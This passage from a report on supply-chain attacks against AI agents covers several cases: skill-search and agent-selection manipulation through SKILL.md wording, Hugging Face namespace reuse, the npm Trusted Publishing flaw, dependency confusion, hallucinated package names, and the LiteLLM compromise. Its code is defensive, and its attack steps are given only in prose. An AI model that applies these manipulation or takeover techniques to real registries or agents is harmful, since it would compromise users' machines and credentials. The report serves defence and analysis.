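As with models on Hugging Face, these shares don't measure a particular user's risk, because an attacker can raise them by uploading 300 copies of a skill that nobody opens.

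### Getting found and chosen

ClawHavoc's publishers relied on volume and tempting names to get their skills found. *Under the Hood of SKILL.md* (Saha, Faghih and Feizi, May 2026), a research demonstration, tested whether an attacker could get the same result by changing a skill's wording. The researchers took 100 ClawHub skills, the top 20 in each of five categories (email, travel, tax, health and prompts), and changed only the text of the SKILL.md file.

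Their first experiment concerned search. Many registries use an embedding model, which turns a text into a list of numbers so that texts with similar meanings get similar lists. The registry ranks skills by how closely their numbers match those of the user's query. Saha and colleagues wrote a program that added up to 20 tokens to the end of a skill's file, about 1% of its length, and kept whichever additions raised its score for a query such as "travel". The added text could be a string of loosely related words that no human reader would find useful.

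The altered skill scored higher than its original in 86% of cases with OpenAI's text-embedding-3-small, the best result of the experiment, but in only 53% and 45% of cases with two open models from the Chinese institute BAAI. When the researchers used OpenAI's model to rank each altered skill against the 20 in its category, the altered skill reached the top ten 80% of the time. An unaltered skill would do so about half the time.

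Real registries use more than embeddings, so the researchers also tried a formula modelled on ClawHub's:

`score = word match + embedding similarity + 0.08 × log(1 + downloads)`

When given 579 downloads, the estimated average on ClawHub, the altered skills beat the baseline in 74% of cases. In a harder test, they had no downloads and competed with the 50 newest skills on ClawHub. The altered skills won 94% of the time at launch but only 40% after an hour, once the others had picked up downloads. Because the score uses the logarithm of downloads, a skill's first ten downloads add as much to its score as growing from 579 to nearly 6,400. An attacker who can fake even a few downloads could therefore undo much of the disadvantage of starting with none.

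In the second experiment, Saha and colleagues offered an agent two skills that did the same thing. They added a sentence to the description of one skill. The sentence praised the skill, told the agent to pick it, or described it as actively maintained or trusted. They wrote five realistic requests for each skill and tried all four kinds of sentence, for a total of 2,000 trials on each of four models: GPT-4.1-mini, GPT-5, Gemma-4-31B and Qwen3-235B. On average, the agents chose the altered skill 77.6% of the time, compared with the 50% expected if they had no preference. Every model preferred the altered skill, and Gemma and Qwen chose it more than 80% of the time.

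The added sentence may not be the only reason agents chose the altered skill. Saha and colleagues state that the two skills differed only in the description, but in their published examples the altered skill also has "-pro" at the end of its name. An agent might prefer `travel-manager-pro` to `travel-manager` because of the name alone. A sample scenario also lists the "-pro" version first, and if that was the usual order, position could have affected the choice too.

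The experiment also made the attacker's task easy. The two skills were otherwise identical, so a claim of recent maintenance was a reasonable way to choose between them, and the user lost nothing if the agent picked the altered one. The 77.6% result shows that wording can decide between equivalent skills, but not whether it could make an agent pass over a better one. The researchers acknowledge that results could differ with other registries, models and ways of choosing. They also tested search and selection separately, so the study doesn't give a success rate for an attack that must succeed at both.

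These attacks matter most when an operator lets the agent find its own skills, as Koi's Alex had been doing before the audit. The shop is less exposed because its configuration specifies `example-author/refund-replies`, so the agent doesn't have to search. But once a malicious skill is installed, its description can still lead the model to use it instead of the one the shop intended.

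## Names that come to point to someone else's artifact

The shop's configuration gives the skill's exact name, `example-author/refund-replies`, but this helps only while the intended publisher controls that name. When publishers close accounts, rename projects or merge with other companies, some platforms let a stranger register the old name. If one does, the shop's unchanged configuration will point to the stranger's file.

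### Model namespace reuse

Saraf and Balassiano (2025), in *Model Namespace Reuse*, their report for Unit 42, found that when a user or organisation deletes its Hugging Face account, the account name becomes available for anyone to register. The new owner can then upload a model under the old model name, recreating the full path that other people's code still requests.

Suppose ExampleLab, which published the shop's model, closes its account. Requests for `ExampleLab/support-8b` now return a 404 ("not found") error, so the shop's agent can't load its model on a new machine. Then an attacker registers `ExampleLab` and uploads a model called `support-8b`. The next request succeeds and returns the attacker's files.

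The outage is the shop's only warning. A developer who finds the model missing in the morning and working in the afternoon may assume that the hub had a temporary fault. If an attacker registers the name quickly enough, the shop won't notice an outage at all.

In the second case there is no outage. Suppose a larger company, BigExample, buys ExampleLab and moves the model to its own account. According to Hugging Face's *Repository Settings*, a person with sufficient rights in both organisations can do this without the hub's help. The hub then uses a 307 code to redirect requests for the old name to the new address. The shop's agent follows the redirect automatically, so nobody has to edit the configuration. BigExample later deletes the empty `ExampleLab` account, and the redirect still works.

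When an attacker registers `ExampleLab` and uploads a model named `support-8b`, the hub stops redirecting the old address because a model exists there again. The shop's agent then gets the attacker's model instead of BigExample's, with no error.

| Stage | Author deleted | Model transferred, then old author deleted |
|---|---|---|
| Before | Original model | Original model |
| Once the account is gone | 404 error | 307 redirect to the original model |
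| Once an attacker has the name | Attacker's model | Attacker's model |

The redirect is convenient, but it makes the problem worse because it leaves maintainers with no reason to update the old name. Without it, every project using that name would have failed on the day of the transfer, and its maintainers would have switched to the new one.

### The demonstrations on Vertex AI and Azure

Saraf and Balassiano tried the deletion case on two large cloud platforms. Google's Vertex AI has a catalogue from which customers can deploy Hugging Face models in a few steps, with a green check mark beside the models Google has verified as deployable. The researchers looked up the models' authors on Hugging Face and found several verified models whose authors' accounts no longer existed. They registered one of the missing authors' names and uploaded a model under the old name, with hidden code that connected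 back to their own server. Once Vertex AI had deployed the model, they could run commands in the container that hosted it. The container had only limited access to the rest of Google's cloud.

The same method worked on Microsoft's Azure AI Foundry, where the researchers obtained the permissions of the endpoint running the model. Those permissions would give an attacker initial access to a customer's Azure environment. Both attacks were demonstrations, and the researchers removed the hidden code afterwards. They do not report any criminal use of the technique.

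The researchers also searched GitHub for code that loads Hugging Face models by name, and found thousands of repositories, some of them well known, that referred to names an outsider could register. The names appeared in default settings, documentation and example notebooks as well as in the main code. Default settings are a particular problem for operators, because a tool can load a model that its user never chose.

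Catalogues that take their models from Hugging Face can spread the problem. Kaggle, a Google-owned site for data science, listed thousands of these models, including several with reusable names, so a Kaggle user could receive an attacker's model without visiting Hugging Face. If a catalogue fetches the model at each deployment, its users are exposed as soon as the takeover happens. If it made its own copy beforehand, they are safe until it refreshes that copy.

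Saraf and Balassiano told Google about the problem in February 2025. Google now scans its catalogue daily for models whose authors' accounts no longer exist and blocks their deployment. This should stop most such takeovers. The scan may miss an attacker who registers a deleted account's name before the next scan, because an account with that name would exist again. To catch that, Google would have to compare the current files or account with the ones it originally verified.

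The researchers also told Microsoft and Hugging Face about the risk, and wrote in September 2025 that it remained. Hugging Face does not appear to have announced a general fix since then. In the forum thread *How to change your username*, a user who tried to work out its rules for renamed organisations in 2026 called the information available online "uncertain overall".

*Your Space is My Zone* (2026) describes a related problem with apps hosted on model hubs. It found nine outside websites that still embedded deleted Hugging Face apps whose addresses an attacker could claim. Hugging Face builds an app's web address by joining the owner's name and the app's name with a hyphen, so `red-panda/chat` and `red/panda-chat` would get the same address. This flaw is separate from the one in model names, so it doesn't show that Hugging Face has left that one unfixed. But until Hugging Face says otherwise,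 operators should assume that strangers can register the names of deleted publishers.

### Pinning a model to a commit

Operators can protect themselves without waiting for the hub. A Hugging Face model is stored in a Git repository, which keeps a history of saved states called commits. Each commit has an ID computed from its files and its history. The loading software fetches the newest commit unless the operator requests a particular one with the `revision` parameter:

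```python
model = AutoModelForCausalLM.from_pretrained(
    "ExampleLab/support-8b",
    revision="<full commit ID recorded at approval>",
)
```

After a takeover, the attacker's new repository does not contain the commit that the shop pinned, so the request fails. If the attacker copies the original repository with its whole history, the request succeeds, but the shop gets the model files it approved. The attacker cannot realistically give different files the same commit ID, so pinning the commit prevents a silent replacement.

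The pin has to be a commit ID. The same parameter also accepts tag names and branch names such as `main`, but whoever controls the repository can move these to other commits. The shop also has to record the ID before the takeover, since a later pin would keep it on the attacker's model.

Each pin covers only one request. The shop's code probably loads the tokenizer, which turns text into the model's input, in a separate call that needs its own `revision`. Some models also use program code from a second repository. Leaving that code unpinned is more dangerous than leaving the weights unpinned, and Hugging Face's Transformers library has a separate parameter for pinning it, `code_revision`.

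A pin can't bring back a deleted model either. For important systems, Saraf and Balassiano recommend scanning the model and then copying it to storage the operator controls. The operator then has to store the copy and decide when to update it, but the agent no longer depends on who owns the model's name on the hub. Customers who deploy from a cloud catalogue may not be able to choose a commit, so they depend on the catalogue's owner to choose it.

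### Freed repository names and npm's Trusted Publishing

GitHub has had trouble with reused names for longer than Hugging Face has. GitHub's redirects work in much the same way, and it warns people who rename a repository not to reuse the old name, because that ends the redirect. Checkmarx's *Attacking the Software Supply Chain with a Simple Rename* describes a flaw, since fixed, that exposed renamed GitHub accounts to takeover. The flaw affected more than 10,000 Go, Swift and PHP packages.

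GitHub's main defence is to retire some names so that nobody can register them again. According to GitHub's *Repo-jacking explained* (2024), it does this only above a certain level of use, because retiring a name inconveniences users who have a good reason to want it. Hugging Face could adopt the same rule, but it would protect the most popular models and not those from small publishers, which some agents may still be using.

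The npm registry also trusted GitHub names, in a place where few users would have looked. Help Net Security's *npm Trusted Publishing flaw exposed 1,500+ npm packages to takeover* (2026) describes the flaw, which the company Bloom Security discovered. Trusted Publishing lets a maintainer release a package without keeping a long-lived publishing token that a thief could steal. It works in three steps:

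1. The maintainer tells npm which GitHub repository may publish the package, and which workflow file (a script that GitHub runs automatically) will do it.
2. When the workflow runs, GitHub issues a signed identity token that states which repository it is running in.
3. npm compares the token with the maintainer's settings. If they match, it issues a publishing credential that expires within minutes.

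The flaw was in the comparison. GitHub gives every repository and owner a permanent number, which stays the same through renames and transfers, and the token included these numbers. But npm compared only the names:

```
npm's check:    repository name in token = recorded name
a safer check:  repository ID in token   = recorded ID
```

If the maintainer had renamed, transferred or deleted the repository, an attacker could often create a new one under the old name and add a workflow file with the expected filename. GitHub would issue a genuine token for the attacker's repository, and npm would accept it. The attacker could then publish a new version of the maintainer's package without stealing any credentials.

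Bloom tested the whole attack on its own package and repositories. It counted more than 1,500 exposed packages, excluding those whose old repository names GitHub had retired. Together they had over a million downloads a month, or several hundred each on average. Most were evidently small, but a small package can still reach many machines as a transitive dependency.

This flaw is harder for users to guard against than model namespace reuse, because users request the right package from the right registry. The name that now belongs to someone else is in the maintainer's publishing settings, which users can't see. Pinning a version would keep out the attacker's release only until they next update the package.

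GitHub, which owns npm, already knew that the new owner of a recycled name could inherit the old owner's access. In April, GitHub (2026) announced that, to prevent this, it was adding permanent numbers to the main identifier in the tokens that workflows present to cloud providers. In its example, `repo:octocat/my-repo` becomes `repo:octocat-123456/my-repo-456789`.

Bloom reported the npm flaw on 6 June. GitHub confirmed it three days later and announced a change on 2 October. A package's first successful release now ties the package's settings to the repository's permanent identity, and settings not validated this way expire after 48 hours. In its statement to Help Net Security, GitHub did not make clear whether it also tied older settings to permanent identities. Nobody knows whether attackers used the flaw before the fix. Bloom says npm's equivalent feature for GitLab has the same weakness.

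Bloom argues that agents increase the risk because they install so many packages, usually without anyone reviewing them. It estimates that agents install about 70 packages a month on a typical machine and close to 350 on a developer's. Adebayo (2026), in *How AI coding tools could amplify software supply-chain attacks*, gives a breakdown with two or three direct installations a day on developer machines. That is fewer than 100 a month, so either the daily figure is per agent or the two figures are inconsistent. Adebayo also reports that Bloom blocked a customer's agent from installing one of the exposed packages. This shows that agents try to install such packages, but it isn't evidence of an attack, because an exposed package is harmless until somebody hijacks it.

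### Private names on public registries

An attacker can also register a name that its publisher has only used privately. Many companies keep in-house packages on a private registry. Suppose the shop has one called `example-order-lookup`. Its installer searches both the private registry and PyPI and takes the highest version it finds. An attacker who learns the name can upload a package with that name and a very high version number to PyPI, and the installer will choose it over the shop's own. This is called dependency confusion. *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* (Churilov, 2026) traces it to a 2021 disclosure by the researcher Alex Birsan.

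In the best-known case in machine learning, somebody uploaded a malicious package called torchtriton to PyPI in December 2022. The nightly test builds of PyTorch, a library that much AI software depends on, needed a package of the same name, which PyTorch's maintainers hosted on their own index. For about five days, Linux users who installed a nightly build with pip, Python's standard installer, got the malicious package instead. It collected files from their machines, including SSH keys, and sent them out. The attack did not affect PyTorch's stable releases. The maintainers renamed the dependency and registered a placeholder on PyPI so that nobody else could take the new name.

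The technique is still in use. SafeDep reports that since June 2025 somebody has published at least 96 packages from 34 throwaway accounts on npm and PyPI, aimed at over 20 named organisations. The packages send out the user's name, the machine's name and the current folder. SafeDep thinks the publisher is probably a researcher looking for bug bounties, because the packages collect so little and some of the account names contain "poc", short for proof of concept.

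The shop could register `example-order-lookup` on PyPI itself, as PyTorch's maintainers did with their new name, or configure its installer to take that package only from the private registry. The second fix works only on machines with that setting, so an agent that installs packages in a fresh container without it could search PyPI again.

### Package names invented by language models

When a language model writes code, it sometimes makes up a plausible package name and adds a command to install it. The command normally fails because no such package exists, but if an attacker has already registered the name, the command succeeds and the attacker's code runs. This attack is called slopsquatting.

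Spracklen and colleagues, whose work Churilov summarises, made the first large measurement of how often models name packages that do not exist. They generated 576,000 code samples with 16 models from 2023 and 2024. On average, 5.2% of the packages named by commercial models did not exist, compared with 21.7% for open models. The models invented 205,474 different names in all.

In April 2026 Churilov gave the same prompts to five newer models: Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5.4-mini, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek V3.2. Between 3.6% and 5.0% of the packages they named did not exist. DeepSeek V3.2, the only open model, had a rate of 4.8%, so the large gap between open and commercial models has closed, at least among the best models. But none of the five did better than GPT-4 Turbo, the best model in the original study, at 3.59%. Stronger models have since come out. The five models also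 could not look anything up, and an agent that checks the registry before naming a package might do much better.

Counting invented names is error-prone. Earlier versions of Churilov's paper compared the names with old package lists, while the November 2026 version checks them against the live registries and gives rates about a fifth lower. The biggest correction was for correct Python code that imports a package under a different name. For example, a program that uses the package PyYAML contains the line `import yaml`, and a simple check would wrongly record "yaml" as an invented package name.

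All five models invented the same 104 package names. These make up under 5% of the 2,282 different names in the study, but they account for 42% of the times a model named a nonexistent package (2,699 of 6,363). An attacker could therefore exploit many of these mistakes by registering only a few names. However, the registries' rules limit which names an attacker can register. PyPI's security team told Churilov that outsiders could register only 41 of the more than 100 Python names on an earlier version of the list.

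Attackers seem slow to claim these names. Within about six months, somebody had registered 25 of the 2,282. At least one contained malware. Churilov did not inspect most of the others, and some may belong to researchers or defenders. Churilov had also accidentally published the list of shared names, which allowed a test of whether publication attracts attackers. In the main comparison, nobody had registered any of 87 published names, compared with 2 of 101 similar unpublished ones. The groups were too small to detect an increase of less than roughly tenfold, so the result is only mildly reassuring.

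The models also suggested at least 23 names that had hosted malware before the registries removed it. The attackers may have picked some of these names because they resembled real packages, not because language models might suggest them.

### Invented names in skills

A package name invented by a language model can reach everyone who copies a skill containing it, whereas one in a chat answer usually reaches a single user. In *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*, Eriksen, a researcher at the security company Aikido, reports that 237 GitHub repositories contained instructions for agents to install react-codeshift, an npm package that had never existed. Eriksen registered the name on 14 January 2026, before an attacker could, and published an empty package. Aikido traced the name to a single upload of 47 skills written by a language model, which had apparently merged the names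 of two real packages, jscodeshift and react-codemod. People then copied, adapted and translated the skills without checking that the package existed.

The empty package soon had downloads, and Eriksen attributes some of them to agents following the skills. Some probably came from security scanners, like the machines that installed Claude Mythos 5's package.

The `npx` launcher makes this kind of mistake easy because developers often give it a command's name, which can differ from the name of the package that provides the command. The package react-styleguidist provides a command called `styleguidist`. A developer who has the package installed can safely run `npx styleguidist`, but on a machine without it, `npx` looks for a package called styleguidist, which for a long time nobody had registered. Aikido searched the whole npm registry for such commands and claimed 14 of the names in July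 2025. The styleguidist package alone had 805 downloads. People can make this mistake without a language model, but an agent that runs commands from old documentation is also likely to make it.

Models also invent the names of skills. Yuan, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *Skills That Don't Exist*, sent 15,000 requests for skill recommendations to 12 set-ups (4 plain models and 8 agents). They counted a name as invented only if they could not find it in the skill registries or on GitHub. Every set-up invented names, at rates from 6.5% to 62.0%, and together they produced 5,669 different ones. Nearly all the set-ups could search the web, but this didn't solve the problem because many of the invented names were those of real tools, such as `visual-studio-code`. A search confirms that the tool exists, but not that anyone has published a skill with that name.

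These rates are far higher than Churilov's 3.6% to 5.0%, but the two studies count differently. Churilov counted every mention of a package, while Yuan and colleagues counted each different name once, so a real skill that an agent recommended a hundred times counts the same as an invented one it recommended once. Their requests were also hard. A third came from forum posts, many of which asked for a plugin or tool for which no skill existed. The average rate was 43.1% on the forum requests and 29.4% on requests written from the descriptions of real skills.

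Repetition matters more to an attacker than the overall rate, and the results on repetition are more worrying. Claude Sonnet 4.6 repeated its most common invented name 7.8 times out of 10. Of the 5,669 names, 410 came from more than one set-up. The invented names were also typically six edits away from any real skill's name, so a filter that looks for misspellings would miss them. *Beware of Agentic Botnets* (2026) reports that coding assistants also invent names for the owners of code repositories, which an outsider can then register.

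Yuan and colleagues tested several defences. Asking the model to review its own answer reduced the average rate only from 40.8% to 33.2%. Retrieval grounding, which gives the model entries from a catalogue of real skills to choose from, reduced it to 3.2%. Even the best-defended system named the right skill only about one time in six, and it was safe mainly because it often gave no answer.

Any defence that looks names up is also weak because it checks only whether a name exists. The lookup protects the user from an invented name only until an attacker registers it, after which the lookup succeeds. An agent that installs only from a list of names and publishers that a person has approved avoids this problem, but somebody has to maintain the list.

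## Unpinned versions and the LiteLLM compromise

A package name can belong to the right publisher and still resolve to a malicious file if an attacker releases a new version under it. This happened on 24 March 2026 to LiteLLM, the gateway library that passes an agent's requests to model providers. The attackers uploaded two malicious versions, and six minutes after the second upload, an old MCP server downloaded that version to an engineer's laptop.

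### Version ranges and lock files

A Python package comes with a list of the other packages it needs and the versions of each that it will accept. The installer normally takes the newest version that satisfies everyone's conditions. FutureSearch's *LiteLLM Hack* gives examples of how the wording of a requirement decided who was at risk when the malicious versions, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8, were the newest on PyPI:

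| Requirement | Could the installer choose a malicious version? |
|---|---|
| `litellm==1.80.0` | No |
| `litellm>=1.0,<1.82` | No |
| `litellm>=1.80` | Yes |
| `litellm>=1.0,<2.0` | Yes |
| `litellm` | Yes |

The upper limit in the fourth requirement, `<2.0`, keeps out incompatible releases, because publishers by convention raise the first number of a version when a release may break existing code. It doesn't block a malicious release if the attacker gives it the next small version number, which is still within the range.

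Library publishers usually specify a range of versions for each dependency because a Python environment can hold only one version of each package. If one library required exactly version 1.80.0 of a package and another required exactly 1.81.0, nobody could install the two libraries together. Whoever builds the final application then chooses the exact version.

A developer can pin versions with a lock file, which lists the exact version and hash of every package the installer selected, including transitive dependencies. Later installs then use those same versions. PyPI's *Incident Report* warns that the output of the common command `pip freeze` isn't a lock file, because it records names and versions but no hashes.

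A lock file protects only the installs that use it. An MCP server publisher's lock file protects the publisher's own test machines, but when a user installs the published server, the package manager usually selects dependency versions again from the allowed ranges.

### What a launcher installs

When the launchers `uvx` and `npx` start a tool server and have no usable copy in their cache, they choose a new version of every package the server needs, directly or indirectly.

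Suppose the invented shop requests `example-mailbox-mcp@2.3.1` instead of the newest version. That server needs `example-mail-parser`, version 1.4 or later. The shop will now get the same mailbox server every time, but the launcher can still install a parser version that an attacker uploaded that morning. The parser runs in the same process as the server and can read the same mailbox token.

The shop can close the gap by installing the server once from a lock file and having the configuration start that copy directly. The shop then has to decide when to update, which removes most of the convenience of using a launcher.

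### From a vulnerability scanner to a PyPI token

The attack on LiteLLM began with Trivy, an Aqua Security tool that checks software for known vulnerabilities. Aqua had disclosed an earlier breach on 1 March. Help Net Security's *LiteLLM PyPI packages compromised in expanding TeamPCP supply chain attacks* (2026) quotes Aqua's explanation that, after that breach, it replaced its credentials over several days rather than all at once, so an attacker holding one that still worked could have used it to copy the new ones.

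On 19 March a criminal group called TeamPCP released a malicious Trivy 0.69.4. According to The Hacker News (2026), the group also repointed 76 of the 77 version tags of trivy-action, a ready-made step for running Trivy on GitHub, to malicious commits. Projects that requested an old, trusted version by its tag then got malicious code instead. Only projects that had pinned the commit ID were safe from the repointed tags, for the same reason that a commit ID protects a model download.

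LiteLLM ran the scanner Trivy in its build pipeline, the automated system that tests and releases its code. *Security Townhall Updates* (Dholakia and Jaff, 2026), by LiteLLM's chief executive and technology chief, names three contributing causes: the pipeline did not pin Trivy's version, it kept the passwords for publishing releases as permanent secrets in environment variables, and all its steps shared one environment. Trivy could therefore read those secrets, though it needed none of them. Boost Security's *TeamPCP Compromises LiteLLM* counted more than 230 secrets that the scan job could access.

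Boost Security examined a sample of that job's logs from 19 to 24 March and found that the job had installed Trivy 0.69.3, the clean version. The malicious version may have reached LiteLLM another way, such as through a Docker image or a copy that a developer downloaded from GitHub. PyPI and LiteLLM both still trace the stolen token to Trivy, which seems likely, but nobody has publicly identified the machine it came from. The attackers then uploaded both malicious LiteLLM versions straight to PyPI, and neither had a matching release in LiteLLM's GitHub repository.

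### Six minutes from upload to infection

The attackers published version 1.82.7 at 10:39 UTC. They hid its malicious code in the file for LiteLLM's proxy server, so the code ran only if a program imported that part of the library. Thirteen minutes later they published 1.82.8, which also contained a file called `litellm_init.pth`.

Every time Python starts, it checks the installed packages for files ending in `.pth`. These files mostly list additional folders to search for code, but they can also contain a line of code, which Python runs immediately. A package with such a file can therefore run code without being imported, whenever any Python program starts in that environment, even one that has nothing to do with LiteLLM.

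At 10:58, Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, tried to connect to its configured MCP servers on the laptop of Callum McMahon, who works at the AI company FutureSearch. One was a mostly abandoned server of the company's own, which needed LiteLLM and set no upper limit on the version. FutureSearch's *Catching the LiteLLM PyPI Attack* (2026) reconstructs the sequence from Cursor's logs:

```
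Cursor starts its configured tool servers
  → uvx runs futuresearch-mcp-legacy
    → uvx installs 77 packages, including litellm 1.82.8
      → the next Python process runs litellm_init.pth
```

A project on the same laptop also used LiteLLM, but it required a version below 1.77.3 and had 1.70.4 installed, so the attack did not affect it. McMahon had been careful about the code under development but had no reason to think about the old server, which Cursor started automatically.

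The malware collected SSH keys, cloud credentials, passwords in configuration files, cryptocurrency wallets and command history, and tried to send them to the attackers. It also had a bug that froze the laptop. The start-up file launched a second Python process to do the work, but that process read the same file and launched a third, and so on until about 11,000 were running. At 11:07 the malware tried to install a component that would survive a restart, but it had written only an empty file when McMahon forced the machine off two minutes later.

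After the restart, McMahon asked Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code to investigate. It first concluded that the processes were harmless and probably its own. After McMahon rejected that explanation, it found the malicious file at 11:40. At 11:58 it downloaded the package again in an isolated container to confirm that PyPI was still serving it. FutureSearch's *How a Poisoned litellm Package Compromised an MCP Server in Cursor* credits the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy with observing that, without the bug, the malware would have gone unnoticed for much longer.

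Cursor started the server because a configuration file listed it, before any model had chosen a tool or read a tool's description. The attack therefore didn't depend on deceiving a model, and an agent whose model was immune to prompt injection would still have been infected. FutureSearch has since moved to a remote server, which keeps such malicious code off its users' machines but leaves them dependent on whoever runs the server.

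### How long, and how many

The published figures for the attack disagree:

| Source | Time on PyPI | Downloads of the two versions |
|---|---|---|
| LiteLLM | About 40 minutes | Not given |
| FutureSearch | 46 minutes | 46,996 |
| PyPI | 2 hours 32 minutes | Over 119,000 |

LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) counts its 40 minutes from 10:39. FutureSearch's 46 minutes end at 11:25, when it believed PyPI had quarantined the package (blocked it from installation). But McMahon downloaded 1.82.8 from PyPI at 11:58, so the quarantine can't have been in force at 11:25. PyPI's timeline fits this download much better. It puts the first report 1 hour 19 minutes after the upload. If that is counted from the upload of 1.82.7, the report came at 11:58, when McMahon emailed PyPI's security team. The quarantine would then have come at about 13:11. Sonatype's *Compromised litellm PyPI Package Delivers Multi-Stage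 Credential Stealer* also reported, on the day of the attack, that the versions had been available for at least two hours.

PyPI's exposure time is therefore the one to use. FutureSearch's download count may still be correct for the 46 minutes it covers, but they are less than a third of that exposure time. LiteLLM gave a figure of 40 minutes, but more cautiously told users to suspect anything installed up to 16:00.

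Neither download count measures how many machines were infected. Of the 46,996 downloads FutureSearch counted, 14,532 were of version 1.82.7, whose malware ran only if a program imported the proxy. FutureSearch also assumes that the malware ran during installation in all 23,142 cases where the installer pip downloaded version 1.82.8. That assumption is probably too strong, because pip is a Python program that is already running when it writes the new start-up file. The file normally wouldn't run until another Python process started, and a mirror or a security scanner may never start one.

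PyPI used its count to estimate how many people install LiteLLM without pinning it. The package normally has 15 to 20 million installs a week, an average of about 1,700 a minute:

```
1,700 installs a minute × 152 minutes ≈ 258,000 installs
119,000 malicious ÷ 258,000 total     ≈ 46%
```

PyPI puts the share at 40–50%, and the two ends of the weekly figure give 53% and 39%. The estimate assumes that installs ran at their average weekly rate during the attack. The attack happened on a Tuesday, in the middle of the European working day, when installs were probably above average, so the true share may be somewhat lower. Even so, a large share of LiteLLM's users were accepting whatever version was newest.

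Publishers were even less careful. FutureSearch found 2,337 packages on PyPI that depend directly on LiteLLM, and 2,054 of them (88%) allowed the malicious versions. Most of those, 1,388, set only a minimum version. Another 457 packages set an upper limit, but in 383 of them it was too high to exclude the malicious versions. The 88% is a share of packages, while PyPI's 46% is a share of installs. A package's loose range does no harm to a user who installs it from a lock file.

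LiteLLM also publishes its proxy as a Docker image, which bundles the program with everything it needs to run. People who used the official image were unaffected because its build instructions specified exact versions, so the image never included the malicious releases.

### Waiting before installing

Even a lock file would not have helped a developer who refreshed it at 11:30 that morning, because the refresh would have written the malicious version into it, with a correct hash. PyPI recommends a second measure for this, a dependency cooldown, in which the installer ignores any version that is too new:

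`version is eligible only if upload time ≤ now − delay`

The Python installer uv can ignore recent releases through its `exclude-newer` setting, where the value `"P3D"` means three days. PyPI suggests setting it for the whole machine. This matters for agents because a setting in one project's folder may not apply to a tool server that an editor starts on its own.

With a three-day delay on McMahon's laptop, `uvx` would have considered only versions uploaded before 10:58 on 21 March, so it would have skipped both malicious releases and installed an older one. Version 1.82.8 would have become eligible at 10:52 on 27 March, almost 70 hours after PyPI had blocked it. Even a three-hour delay would have been enough for LiteLLM, but not for telnyx, another package that TeamPCP compromised, which PyPI took 3 hours 42 minutes to quarantine.

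In LiteLLM's second compromise of the year, on 21 October, an attacker took over the project's release pipeline and published a malicious version 1.107.0. According to Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026), it stayed on PyPI from 11:39 to 13:23 UTC and again used Python start-up files. A three-day delay in the Python installer would have kept this version out too, but it wouldn't have covered Docker. This time the attacker also published Docker images, and for about two and a half hours the tags `latest`, `main-latest` and `main-stable` all pointed to a malicious one. Pinning inside the image had protected Docker users in March, but it didn't help anyone who requested the image by a movable tag in October.

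Cooldowns delay security fixes as well as malware. SC Media reports that attackers exploited a flaw in LiteLLM's proxy within 36 hours of its disclosure. An operator who waited three days to install the fix would have spent the second half of that time exposed to attacks already under way.

PyPI's answer is to exempt security fixes from the cooldown. Dependabot and Renovate, two tools that propose dependency updates to developers, skip the cooldown for security updates by default, and a developer can set the delay to zero to install a particular version immediately. This works if someone is watching for announcements. When a launcher starts a tool server in the background, nobody is there to apply the exemption, so the operator needs a scanner that reports known flaws in installed packages. The objection is stronger against lock files, which hold back every fix until somebody updates them,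 while a cooldown holds it back for three days.

How much risk the delay adds depends on where the software runs. Attackers could use that flaw only against a LiteLLM proxy they could reach over the network, so a day or two can matter a great deal for a proxy on the public internet. A tool server on one developer's laptop is usually safe from that kind of attack but fully exposed to a malicious update, so waiting is probably safer there.

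Another objection is that a cooldown works only because other people don't use one. In March the first report to PyPI came from a victim, and if everyone had waited three days, everyone might have installed the malware on the fourth day. The October attack weakens this argument. TecnoAndroid's *LiteLLM compromesso* (2026) reports that several security companies detected the malicious release within six minutes of publication, because they scan new packages without waiting for a victim to report a problem. They may not catch a less obvious attack so quickly, and a cooldown doesn't stop malware that goes unnoticed for longer than the delay.

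Attackers can also try to keep a warning from spreading. A researcher opened a public issue about version 1.82.8 on LiteLLM's GitHub page at 11:48. Boost Security found that the attackers, who controlled the chief executive's account, closed it an hour later without comment. Spam accounts then posted 293 of the issue's 334 comments.

### What the attackers took

In August 2026 several security companies published analyses of the stolen data. Hudson Rock examined an archive of 433,909 files and, according to GitGuardian (2026), linked 118,829 build-job records in it to 2,488 organisations. CloudSEK, using its own sources, reported more than 2,500. Kurmi (2026), in *Team PCP Stole 78,330 Secrets From 2,186 Organizations*, counted fewer organisations in CloudSEK's data and found that 157 of them had leaked OpenAI keys.

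Kurmi dates the thefts to the five days from 19 to 24 March, but the malicious LiteLLM versions existed only on 24 March. The data therefore don't support GitGuardian's claim that all of this came from "one 40-minute window", or the many headlines that named LiteLLM alone. Corgea (2026) cites another company, SOCRadar, which thinks many of the named organisations were probably exposed earlier, through Trivy. CloudSEK told The Hacker News that its figure of 434,000 counts captured files and uploads. Corgea describes these as build pipelines, but one pipeline can produce many of them. The number of organisations that lost credentials through LiteLLM specifically is unknown.

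An organisation's appearance in the data also doesn't prove that anyone used its credentials. A few cases of harm are confirmed. Mercor, a company that recruits experts to train AI models, said that the malicious LiteLLM versions had affected it. Checkmarx, a security company, lost control of some of its GitHub repositories through credentials stolen at the Trivy stage. Attackers also took about 92 GB of compressed data from a European Commission cloud account. SANS Internet Storm Center (2026) dates that intrusion to 19 March, five days before the LiteLLM releases, so LiteLLM can't have been the cause.

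Removing a malicious package does not revoke the keys it has already copied. In July the FBI warned that criminals were likely to use credentials from the campaign long after the theft, and TechRadar's *Massive supply-chain attack sees terabytes of data* reported in August that some still worked. Many owners will never be warned, because their records contain working passwords but no company name or email address.

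*Popular AI tool LiteLLM says unrevoked key allowed hackers to target users* (Martin, 2026) reports about 49,000 downloads of version 1.107.0. Attackers were faster in October. Within four and a half hours of the upload, the attacker was trying stolen Amazon cloud credentials to see which AI models they could run at the victims' expense. As of late October, no organisation had publicly confirmed a breach.

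LiteLLM had made its releases more secure after March, including by switching to short-lived publishing credentials, but the second attack used a key that had leaked months earlier. On 27 May, someone at the company accidentally published a configuration file containing the master key to an internal service. The team deleted the file about three hours later but did not revoke the key. On 10 October, an attacker used it to get a token with control over all of LiteLLM's repositories.

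## Tools and skills that change after approval

Thieves published the malicious versions of LiteLLM, but a publisher can also turn its own artifact malicious by waiting until operators have reviewed it and then changing it. Programmers call this weakness "time of check to time of use", because the artifact can change between the moment it is checked and the moment it is used.

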